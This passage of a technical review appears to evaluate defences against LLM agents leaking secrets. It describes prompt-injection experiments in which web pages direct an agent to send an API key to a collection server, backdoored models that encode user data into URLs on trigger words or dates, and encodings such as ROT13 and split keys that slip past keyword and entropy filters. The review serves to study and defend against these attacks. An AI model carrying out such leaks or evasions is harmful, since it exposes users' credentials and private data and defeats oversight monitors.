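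Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo, a benchmark that measures task completion and resistance to prompt injection. With suitable policies enforced, FIDES stopped every attack. It also completed more tasks than a basic agent design using the same model, by 8% with GPT-4o and 16% with OpenAI's o1. With the policy checks turned off, its extra machinery reduced task completion by 6.3%. A team has to write the policies, and without them the attacks worked on FIDES too.

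CaMeL, another system of this kind, completes 77% of AgentDojo's tasks, compared with 84% for an undefended agent, according to Singh and Srinivasa's summary.

### Leak rates and task costs

FlowSeal, which Shim and colleagues built, combines origin tracking with a content check. It labels sensitive records by owner and intercepts every tool call that writes or shares data. If the agent has read a protected record and the recipient is unknown, a separate language model checks the proposed output and returns `SAFE` or `BLOCKED`. This model receives only the protected records and the proposed output, so the attacker's messages never reach it.

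Li and colleagues tested a simpler guard that blocked the agent from writing planted tokens it had read on web pages. *GuardianAgentFlow* (2026) describes a system that splits the work of protecting private details in web requests among several model calls.

| System | Compared with | Leak rate, before and after | Tasks completed, before and after |
|---|---|---|---|
| Shim and colleagues' FlowSeal | Privacy rules in the agent's prompt | 52.2%, 0.5% | 44.7%, 72.4% |
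| Li and colleagues' guard | No guard | 79.5%, 51.3% | 76.9%, 79.5% |
| *GuardianAgentFlow* | A single model call | 14.3%, 0.0% | 67.2%, 87.3% |

The leak rates aren't comparable between rows because FlowSeal's rate is a share of sensitive items, the guard's a share of runs, and GuardianAgentFlow's a share of requests. The guard's test covered only 39 pairs of runs with one model, too few to show whether task completion changed.

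FlowSeal's results depend heavily on its content check. When Shim and colleagues replaced the check with one that always blocked unknown recipients, 1.3% of sensitive items leaked, but the agent completed no legitimate tasks. When the replacement always allowed unknown recipients, the leak rate rose to 24.9%. Origin tracking can therefore identify which requests need checking, but a model still has to judge whether the text reveals anything. Paraphrase is the main way to evade that model, so this approach shares the weakness of content matching, though to a lesser degree.

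FlowSeal also reduces sharing that the owner would allow. When owners were willing to consent, it delivered 32.7% of the requested items, compared with 61.0% to 85.6% for four other defences, mostly because the agent asked for consent less often. It added about $0.017 to the cost of a run and increased the delay by 37%. A different set of prompt rules completed 75.9% of legitimate tasks, slightly more than FlowSeal, but leaked 31.8% of items in the same attack.

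Shim and colleagues excluded prompt injection from their tests. Their attackers instead disguised requests for data as ordinary work, such as filling in a section of a shared document. Fetching a web page looks like reading data rather than sharing it, so a developer would have to classify it as an outbound call before FlowSeal could check the URL.

A browser agent called INTACT prevents some leaks by limiting the data available to model calls that an attacker can influence. The call that decides what to type into one element of a page isn't given private data from elsewhere on the page. *What It Is, Not What It Says* (2026) reports 546 attacks that tried to make an agent copy page data into the attacker's input box. An ordinary agent copied the data in 345 of them. INTACT copied it in none, though it once proposed typing part of it.

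Origin tracking can also help investigators after a leak. Cai and colleagues' NeuroTaint reads an agent's log and traces which outside text influenced a tool call. If the text doesn't appear in the call, NeuroTaint assesses whether the agent would still have made the call with neutral text in its place. In the hiking example, this could connect the image request to the stranger's comment. Cai and colleagues tested NeuroTaint on a benchmark of 400 scenarios, which they designed around the kinds of influence it is meant to detect. It achieved 92.1% precision and 93.5% recall. Its F1 score, which combines the two, was 0.928, compared with 0.522 for FIDES. The analysis needs the complete log of the agent's run, so it can't block the request that leaks the data.

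## Testing the filters and setting alert thresholds

The evidence for each signal so far comes from different data: source code for entropy, DNS lookups for volume, and a few published attacks for exact-URL checks. Lan and colleagues at eBay instead tested several filters on the same leaking agent. Network filters stopped every leak, while warnings to the model stopped fewer than half. Their advice to control the network rather than rely on the model is probably right, but the filter results support it much less than they appear to.

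### The eBay experiment

The agent ran on qwen2.5:7b, an open model with 7 billion parameters. Each run began when a user asked for a summary of a web page. The software fetched the page and placed its text in the model's context, next to an API key. The page contained instructions to send the key to a collection server, which recorded each request.

Lan and colleagues put the instructions in the page's title, its metadata, its body or the text of a link. The agent reached the page directly or through redirects, and was instructed to give the key whole or in four pieces. There were 16 configurations, each run 30 times, for a total of 480 runs. The counts below are calculated from the published rates.

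| Instructions asked for | Runs | Runs that contacted the attacker's server | Runs counted as leaking in the first request |
|---|---|---|---|
| The whole key | 240 | 238 (99%) | 232 (97%) |
| Four pieces | 240 | 185 (77%) | 63 (26%) |
| Total | 480 | 423 (88.1%) | 295 (61%) |

In 95% of the 423 successful attacks, the answer on the user's screen was harmless, so a monitor that read only final answers would have missed about 400 of them. This is the most useful result for deciding where to put a monitor, and it doesn't depend on the filters.

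The 88.1% figure is harder to apply elsewhere because the key was already in the context, the system prompt contained little besides the tool format, and the model was small. Lan and colleagues say the setup favours the attacker, though they also argue that a more capable model might carry out injected instructions more reliably.

### What splitting the key did

Splitting reduced the share of runs that contacted the server from 99% to 77%, making the attack less reliable. It is unclear how often the attacker received a usable key.

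Lan and colleagues define Leak@k as the share of runs in which sensitive data appears in any of the first k requests. For split keys, they report a Leak@1 of 26.3% and a Leak@3 of 15.8%. Under their definition, Leak@3 cannot be lower than Leak@1, because a run that leaks in its first request has also leaked within its first three. Either one of the figures is wrong or the code measured something else.

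The definition also counts any fragment of the secret as a leak, yet only 63 of the 185 runs that contacted the server counted as leaks in the first request. In the other 122, the model may have sent wrong or empty pieces, which would mean the attack failed, or the code may not have recognised correct four-character pieces, which would mean the attack worked and only the measurement failed. The paper defines a completion rate, the share of runs in which all four pieces arrive, which would help distinguish these cases, but doesn't report it. The pieces in its worked example, `SECR`, `ET_A`, `PI_K` and `EY_1`, also spell only the first 16 characters of the 20-character key.

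Lan and colleagues conclude that splitting the key gets it past simple content filters. That is very likely true, because none of the four pieces contains a word on their keyword list. But they tested the filters only on the whole key.

### Nine conditions, thirty runs each

The filter tests used one configuration, with the instructions in the page's body, direct delivery and the whole key.

| Condition | What it does | Runs that attempted the request | Runs that leaked |
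|---|---|---|---|
| No defence | | 30 | 30 |
| Warning in the system prompt | Tells the model to ignore instructions in web content | 20 | 20 |
| Tags | Mark web content as untrusted | 30 | 30 |
| Warning and tags | Both of the above | 17 | 17 |
| Allowlist | Permits four hosts, matched exactly | 30 | 0 |
| Redirect detection | Blocks bare IP addresses, eight top-level domains such as `.xyz`, and paths containing words such as `collect` or `steal` | 25 | 0 |
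| Keyword filter | Blocks URLs containing words such as `api_key`, `secret` or `token` | 7 | 0 |
| Entropy filter | Blocks parameter values over 10 characters long with entropy above 4.0 | 0 | 0 |
| All combined | | 0 | 0 |

Lan and colleagues chose the attacker's server, `evil-collector.net`, because it was clearly outside any reasonable allowlist, so the list was expected to block it. Blocking it 30 times shows that the code worked, but not how the list would handle a permitted relay or a shared storage host, the routes that real attacks on allowlists have used.

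The next filter, misleadingly named redirect detection, matches suspicious addresses and words. It caught the attack's requests because their path, `/collect`, contains the blocked word `collect`. If the attacker had named the path `/img`, the requests would probably have got through, since their domain ended in `.net`, which the filter doesn't block.

The keyword filter had a similar advantage, because the paper's example key, `SECRET_API_KEY_12345`, contains two of the listed words. A calendar entry, a card number or a typical random access key contains none of them.

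The entropy filter, however, should have let the example key through, since the key scores only 3.85. The filter would have barely caught an unpadded Base64 copy of the key, which scores 4.01.

In the table, attempts fell from 30 out of 30 to 7 with the keyword filter and to 0 with the entropy filter. This is strange because the filters run after the model has written its tool call, so they can't affect whether it writes the first one. Chance can't plausibly explain the drop to 0.

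Lan and colleagues suggest that the model avoids random-looking parameters when it is monitored, but it would have to know about the monitoring first. They attribute the low keyword figure to the model sometimes encoding the key, but encoded requests would have passed the keyword filter and reached the server, and the table records no leaks. Perhaps the prompt differed between conditions, or the code failed to record some requests. Whatever the cause, the entropy filter had nothing to block in this test, so the reported 100% reduction is no evidence that it works.

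Running the agent once without filters, recording its requests and then applying every filter to the same recording would avoid this problem.

### The missing false alarm rate

Lan and colleagues also report a false positive rate of 0.0%, because the agent never contacted the attacker's server in 120 runs with harmless pages. This shows that the agent doesn't leak spontaneously, as expected, since a harmless page doesn't give it the attacker's address. Measuring the filters' false positive rate would instead require counting how many legitimate requests each one blocks.

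Even if 120 legitimate requests had passed through a filter without a false alarm, the result would be weak. A filter with a true false positive rate of f lets n independent requests through with probability (1 − f)<sup>n</sup>. Setting this to 5% gives the highest rate that is still reasonably compatible with a clean result:

f = 1 − 0.05<sup>1/n</sup>, or roughly 3/n

If a filter raises no false alarms on 120 harmless test requests, its true false alarm rate could still be as high as about 2.5%, at 95% confidence. At that rate, an application that makes 50,000 harmless requests a day would get more than 1,200 false alarms a day.

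*The Framing Gap* reports a false-alarm rate of zero but calls that result "near-definitional". The protected value in its test is a made-up token that never occurs in normal text, so searching for the token couldn't raise a false alarm. A fairer test would protect a passphrase made of ordinary words, or a value that the agent legitimately sends to a second host.

### Encodings the filter's author didn't expect

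*The Framing Gap* also tested two content filters on an agent running GPT-4o. The simpler one blocked any request to an untrusted host that contained the token. The other ran the same check after removing separators and undoing Base64, hexadecimal and reversal. ROT13 replaces each letter with the one 13 places later in the alphabet, and the Caesar shift used here moves each letter three places instead. The table gives the share of 20 trials in which the token leaked.

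| How the model was to write the token | No filter | Plain search | Search after decoding |
|---|---|---|---|
| Unchanged | 40% | 0% | 0% |
| Reversed | 100% | 100% | 0% |
| Hexadecimal | 75% | 75% | 0% |
| Base64 | 50% | 50% | 0% |
| With hyphens | 50% | 50% | 0% |
| With spaces | 25% | 25% | 0% |
| ROT13 | 100% | 100% | 100% |
| Caesar shift | 0% | 0% | 0% |
| Base32 | 0% | 0% | 0% |

The decoding filter stopped every leak that used an encoding it was designed to decode, but none of the ROT13 leaks. Adding ROT13 to the decoder would be easy, but an attacker could then switch to another encoding. The last two rows don't show whether either filter works, because nothing leaked even without a filter. In a separate check, GPT-4o failed to write Base32 correctly in ten attempts. It could write the Caesar shift but didn't in response to that page.

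The wording of the attack mattered as much as the encoding. Five versions of one injected instruction succeeded between 0% and 100% of the time, with an average of 52%. An attacker who tried three of them would find one that worked about 96% of the time. Results also varied between identical experiments, with 51 leaks in 160 trials in one and 64 in another. Thirty runs with a single page, as in the eBay filter tests, are therefore a better measure of that page than of the attack in general.

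### Leaks trained into the model

In all these tests, the instruction to leak came from a web page. *Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your Data* (Zhang and Pei, 2026) describes an attack, Back-Reveal, that trains the leak into the model. The fine-tuned model behaves normally until a question contains certain ordinary words, such as "OBS" and "Twitch" in a question about streaming. It then reads the user's details from its stored memory, encodes them in Base64url, and requests a URL with the encoded text in a query parameter. The server poses as a documentation or search service, so the request looks like a normal lookup.

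Zhang and Pei tried this with three open models of 7 to 20 billion parameters. With triggers of two or three words, the models made the request for about 97% of triggered questions.

Zhang and Pei didn't test an encoding detector, which is meant to find things like a long Base64url value sent to an unfamiliar host. They write that such detectors produce high false positive rates because applications encode parameters for many legitimate reasons. This is plausible, since many pre-signed links and sign-in redirects look encoded, but they give no data for it. The false positive rates they report, from 0.1% to 1.2%, measure how often the hidden behaviour started after an ordinary question.

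Zhang and Pei recommend allowlists, limits on volume and parameter entropy, and alerts for Base64-like values, but leave testing these to future work. They did test two commercial-style guardrails, NeMo Guardrails and LLM Guard, and between 81% and 87% of the attacker's steering responses got through. Both guardrails examined text coming into the agent, so the result doesn't apply to filters on outgoing requests.

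Unlike the other experiments, *SilentCall* (Pallakonda, Hindsbo and colleagues, 2026) reports a false positive rate measured on thousands of legitimate actions. The researchers also trained open models to leak data. Once the system date reached 2026, the agent added a second command to the one the user needed, which uploaded the user's credentials to a storage bucket. At the model's most predictable setting, its answers never mentioned the upload.

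Pallakonda and colleagues tested a two-stage monitor on 10,007 shell commands. A small classifier examines each command in about 4 milliseconds. If it rates the command as critical, a language model uses the conversation to check whether the user's request justifies the command. Every malicious command was the same upload, so the detection rate shows only that the monitor recognised one payload in many different conversations. The false positive rates are more informative because the legitimate commands covered thousands of different actions, but the rates for URLs might be quite different.

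### Why a 1% false positive rate is too high

Suppose an application makes 50,000 requests a day, of which 5 are malicious, and a filter has 90% recall and a 1% false positive rate. The filter catches 4.5 malicious requests a day on average and flags 500 of the 49,995 legitimate ones. Its precision is 4.5 out of 504.5, or 0.9%. At five minutes per alert, checking them all would take 42 hours of work a day.

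With M malicious and L legitimate requests, recall r and false positive rate f, precision P is:

P = rM / (rM + fL)

Rearranging this gives the highest false positive rate that still achieves a chosen precision:

f = rM(1 − P) / (PL)

For a precision of 50%, f is 4.5 / 49,995, or about 0.009%. The last column of the next table uses the 3/n rule to show how many legitimate requests a filter must be tested on, with no false alarms, to demonstrate a false-alarm rate of f.

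| Target precision | False alarms a day | Highest false positive rate | Test requests needed |
|---|---|---|---|
| 10% | 40.5 | 0.081% | About 3,700 |
| 50% | 4.5 | 0.009% | About 33,000 |
| 90% | 0.5 | 0.001% | About 300,000 |

Here are the SilentCall monitors at the same volume, assuming that their rates carried over and that they caught nearly all of the 5 malicious requests:

| Monitor | Measured false positive rate | False alarms a day | Precision |
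|---|---|---|---|
| Classifier alone | 16.35% | 8,174 | 0.06% |
| Classifier, then Qwen3.5-2B | 1.73% | 865 | 0.6% |
| Classifier, then gpt-5-nano | 0.67% | 335 | 1.5% |

Pallakonda and colleagues consider the classifier too noisy to deploy alone and recommend the version with Qwen3.5-2B. That version removes nine out of ten false alarms, but the remaining 865 a day would be too many for people to read. A monitor with this error rate would have to act automatically, for instance by refusing a command and letting the agent try a different one.

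Nobody knows how many malicious requests a typical application makes, but 5 a day is probably far too high an estimate for most. If an application makes one a month, even a filter that meets the 0.009% false-positive rate would raise about 150 false alarms for each malicious request.

### A test procedure

1. Record several weeks of real requests without blocking any.
2. Label them as legitimate, malicious or unclear.
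3. Create synthetic leaks that vary in size, encoding and destination.
4. Run every filter, alone and in combination, on the same recorded requests and synthetic leaks.
5. Choose thresholds using the earlier weeks, then measure false alarms in the final week.

An application that makes 50,000 requests a day will make 1.4 million in four weeks, too many to label individually. Most will go to a few endpoints, so reviewers can label each endpoint's ordinary traffic as a group. They should then individually review requests that a filter flagged, requests to rarely used hosts, and a random sample of the rest. The recording should include a month-end, when applications often make requests that don't occur in other weeks.

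The random sample can't show that the traffic contains no attacks. If reviewers examine 3,000 unflagged requests and find nothing wrong, up to 0.1% of the traffic could still be malicious, which would be 50 requests a day. Recall therefore has to be measured with the synthetic leaks.

| What to vary | Examples |
|---|---|
| Value | Six-digit code, 20-character key, calendar entry, 200-character summary |
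| Form | Plain text, Base64url, hexadecimal, reversed, ROT13, paraphrase |
| Place in the URL | Subdomain, path, query parameter |
| Destination | Unlisted host, permitted relay, stranger's space on a shared host |
| Pacing | One request, four pieces, one character per request |

These options make up to 648 combinations. A script can write most of the URLs and pass them straight to the filters to test which ones each filter recognises. The team also has to make the real agent send some requests, using invented secrets and a server the team controls, to check whether its requests reach the filters. Those runs should use several prompt wordings, and the report should state how many leaks occurred with the filters off. Without that number, readers can't tell whether a filter stopped a leak or the model never attempted it.

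Whoever builds the filter should not know some of the encodings used to test it. *Caught in the Act(ivation)* (2026), which detects an agent leaking planted credentials, kept a set of disguises out of its detector's training, including ROT13, lookalike letters, paraphrase and partial copies. To test slow leaks, it used 50 invented conversations of 20 turns, each with four to eight small attempts. It measured false positives on 1,000 harmless prompts that resembled the attack tasks. These prompts are a much better test than 120 runs that couldn't have triggered a filter, although no false alarms in 1,000 would still allow a rate of 0.3%, or 150 a day in the example above. A team can get a similar separation by asking a colleague who hasn't seen the filter's code to choose a third of the encodings.

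A URL filter needs a separate test set of harmless requests that resemble exfiltration, such as pre-signed links, sign-in redirects, chart links and searches that contain the user's name. *Detecting Shadow AI* (2026) took this approach with detectors for unapproved AI agents on company computers, testing them on 12 agents and 9 harmless workloads, some of which were chosen because they behave like agents. Two rule-based detectors each flagged 4 of the 9 harmless workloads, for precisions of 0.69 and 0.71. A third detector made no mistakes, but with so few cases, the exact 95% confidence intervals are 74% to 100% for its recall and 0% to 34% for its false positive rate.

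*Detecting Shadow AI* points out that precision on such a test depends on how many lookalikes it contains. Adding nine more would lower a rule's measured precision without changing the rule. The lookalikes are for finding where a filter fails, but its false positive rate should come from the recorded traffic.

### Combining signals

A team can require two signals to agree before raising an alert, or accept either one. Suppose an unlisted destination has 90% recall and a 1% false positive rate, while a match with private text has 60% recall and a 0.5% rate. (All four figures are invented.) If the two made their mistakes independently, the results would be:

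| Rule | Recall | False positive rate | False alarms a day |
|---|---|---|---|
| Either signal | 96% | 1.495% | 747 |
| Both signals | 54% | 0.005% | 2.5 |

The procedure runs combinations of signals on recorded traffic instead of multiplying their individual rates, because the signals aren't independent. For example, when a user asks the agent to find an appointment at a clinic it has never contacted, the request goes to an unlisted host and contains private text, so both signals are wrong. Requiring both signals for an alert would miss almost half the leaks. It would produce only 2.5 false alarms a day, with 52% precision, if the signals were independent. If a fifth of the false text matches went to unlisted hosts, there would be 50 false alarms a day and precision would fall to 5%.

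Some alert conditions reduce false alarms without missing many leaks. For example, trackr.live proposes an alert when the page that displays the assistant's answers loads an image from an unlisted host. Limiting the alert to images loaded by that page excludes other traffic, such as the user's own browsing, without excluding leaks through images. Leaks through tools need a separate rule because this one misses them.

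*Block webhook.site exfil*, a guide in the documentation for Cisco's agent security software DefenseClaw, describes a similar combination. It sets up a firewall rule against known request-inspection services and a separate check for model output that contains a secret and mentions one of these services. The guide doesn't give error rates.

Two-stage checks like SilentCall's also require two signals to agree, and they too can lose detections. When Pallakonda and colleagues used a smaller model, Qwen3.5-0.8B, as the judge, it approved two uploads that the classifier had correctly flagged. Prompt injection would add a further risk, because the conversation may include the attacker's explanation of why the request is necessary, and this might lead the judge to approve it. The conversations in SilentCall contained no hostile text because the malicious behaviour came from the model's weights. FlowSeal's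 design seems safer against prompt injection because it withholds the attacker's messages from the judge.

### Blocking, asking or logging

Blocking is worthwhile if the expected harm from a leak exceeds the expected harm from wrongly blocking a request. For an alert with precision P, a leak must do more than (1 − P)/P times as much harm as a wrongly blocked request. At 0.9% precision, the ratio is about 110. A missing image in a chat answer does almost no harm, so blocking images from unlisted hosts is justified even with poor precision. Preventing an accounts assistant from opening a supplier's invoice is more disruptive, so the same precision may be too low for blocking those requests.

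| Action | When it suits | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Block | Legitimate requests almost never match, or losing one does little harm | A planted marker value in a URL; an image from an unlisted host |
| Hold for confirmation | The request may be legitimate, and the user can tell | Private text going to a new site during a booking |
| Log | The signal is weak by itself | High entropy or unusual length on a permitted host |

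The application must not send a held request until the user answers. The prompt should show the destination and the decoded data, as in "Send *Dr Lee, 12 June* to collector.example?", because the user can't judge an encoded URL. The prompt only works if the user reads it, so prompts have to be rare. A team might set a limit of one prompt per user per week and adjust the rule until it stays within that limit on recorded traffic.

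For signals with a score, such as length or entropy, the team can base the threshold on the number of alerts it has time to read. If it can check 20 a day, the false positive rate can be no higher than 20 out of 49,995 legitimate requests, or 0.04%. The team sorts the recorded legitimate requests by score, sets the threshold so that 20 a day exceed it on average, and then measures what share of the synthetic leaks score above it. If only 10% do, the signal isn't worth an alert on its own, and lowering the threshold would create more alerts than the team can read.

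Session totals can trigger different actions at different levels. *Caught in the Act(ivation)* estimates how much information an agent's output has revealed so far and compares the total with a budget. At 90% of the budget it removes the most suspicious parts of the output, and at 100% it blocks it entirely. A URL monitor could similarly ask for confirmation when the total is just below the level at which it blocks requests.

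### Handling an alert

If the monitor flags the request that carries "Dr Lee, 12 June" to collector.example, the analyst should first disable the agent's network tools for that session. This applies even if the monitor blocked the request, because the injected instructions are still in the model's context and the agent may try another route. Cisco also reports attempts that its firewall has already stopped. The analyst shouldn't open the URL to see what is there, because that would deliver the data if the monitor had blocked the request.

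Next, the analyst needs to determine whether the request was sent. A block recorded before execution means that this request wasn't sent, while a proxy record of any response from the server, even an error, means that it was. The analyst should save the session's log entries before their normal deletion date and record the model's name and version with them.

trackr.live advises treating proof that the data was sensitive as a question for after the block, not as a condition for acting. If the value decodes, the analyst knows what leaked. If it doesn't, its length at least limits what it could contain. Sixty characters of Base64, for example, have room for a password but not for a whole document. It is reasonable to assume that any secret that fits has leaked.

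One request may be part of a longer leak, so the analyst should search the session for other requests to the same domain, including small ones that raised no alert. The analyst should then look for other users whose agents contacted that domain or read the same page. If the hiking page caused the request, it may have affected everyone whose assistant summarised it.

The cause of a flagged request is usually in the text the model had read. If that text contains no suspicious instructions, the user may have asked for the request, or the agent may have copied the data carelessly, as Li and colleagues' agents did without any attacker. With a downloaded model, the analyst should also consider whether it was trained to leak data, as in Back-Reveal and SilentCall. The analyst can test for this by replaying the session with invented data in an isolated environment, on both the suspect model and one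 from another publisher. The replay has to keep the original wording and system date, because either could trigger the leak.

The team should immediately replace any passwords and access keys that may have leaked, because waiting for certainty could do more harm than replacing them unnecessarily. Private information, such as the details of a doctor's appointment, can't be replaced, so the team has to tell the user that it may have leaked. The team should also remove the poisoned page or email from everything the agent can retrieve and check the agent's memory, where the ZombieAgent attack stored instructions that remained after the original conversation.

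Finally, the analyst records a verdict of leak, false alarm or undetermined. A value that nobody could decode should be marked undetermined, because counting it as a false alarm would make the filter look worse than it is and might persuade the team to loosen it. Confirmed leaks and false alarms both go into the test set. Before adding a host to the allowlist to stop a false alarm, the team should check whether that host fetches URLs on behalf of others, then rerun the synthetic leaks with the new entry.
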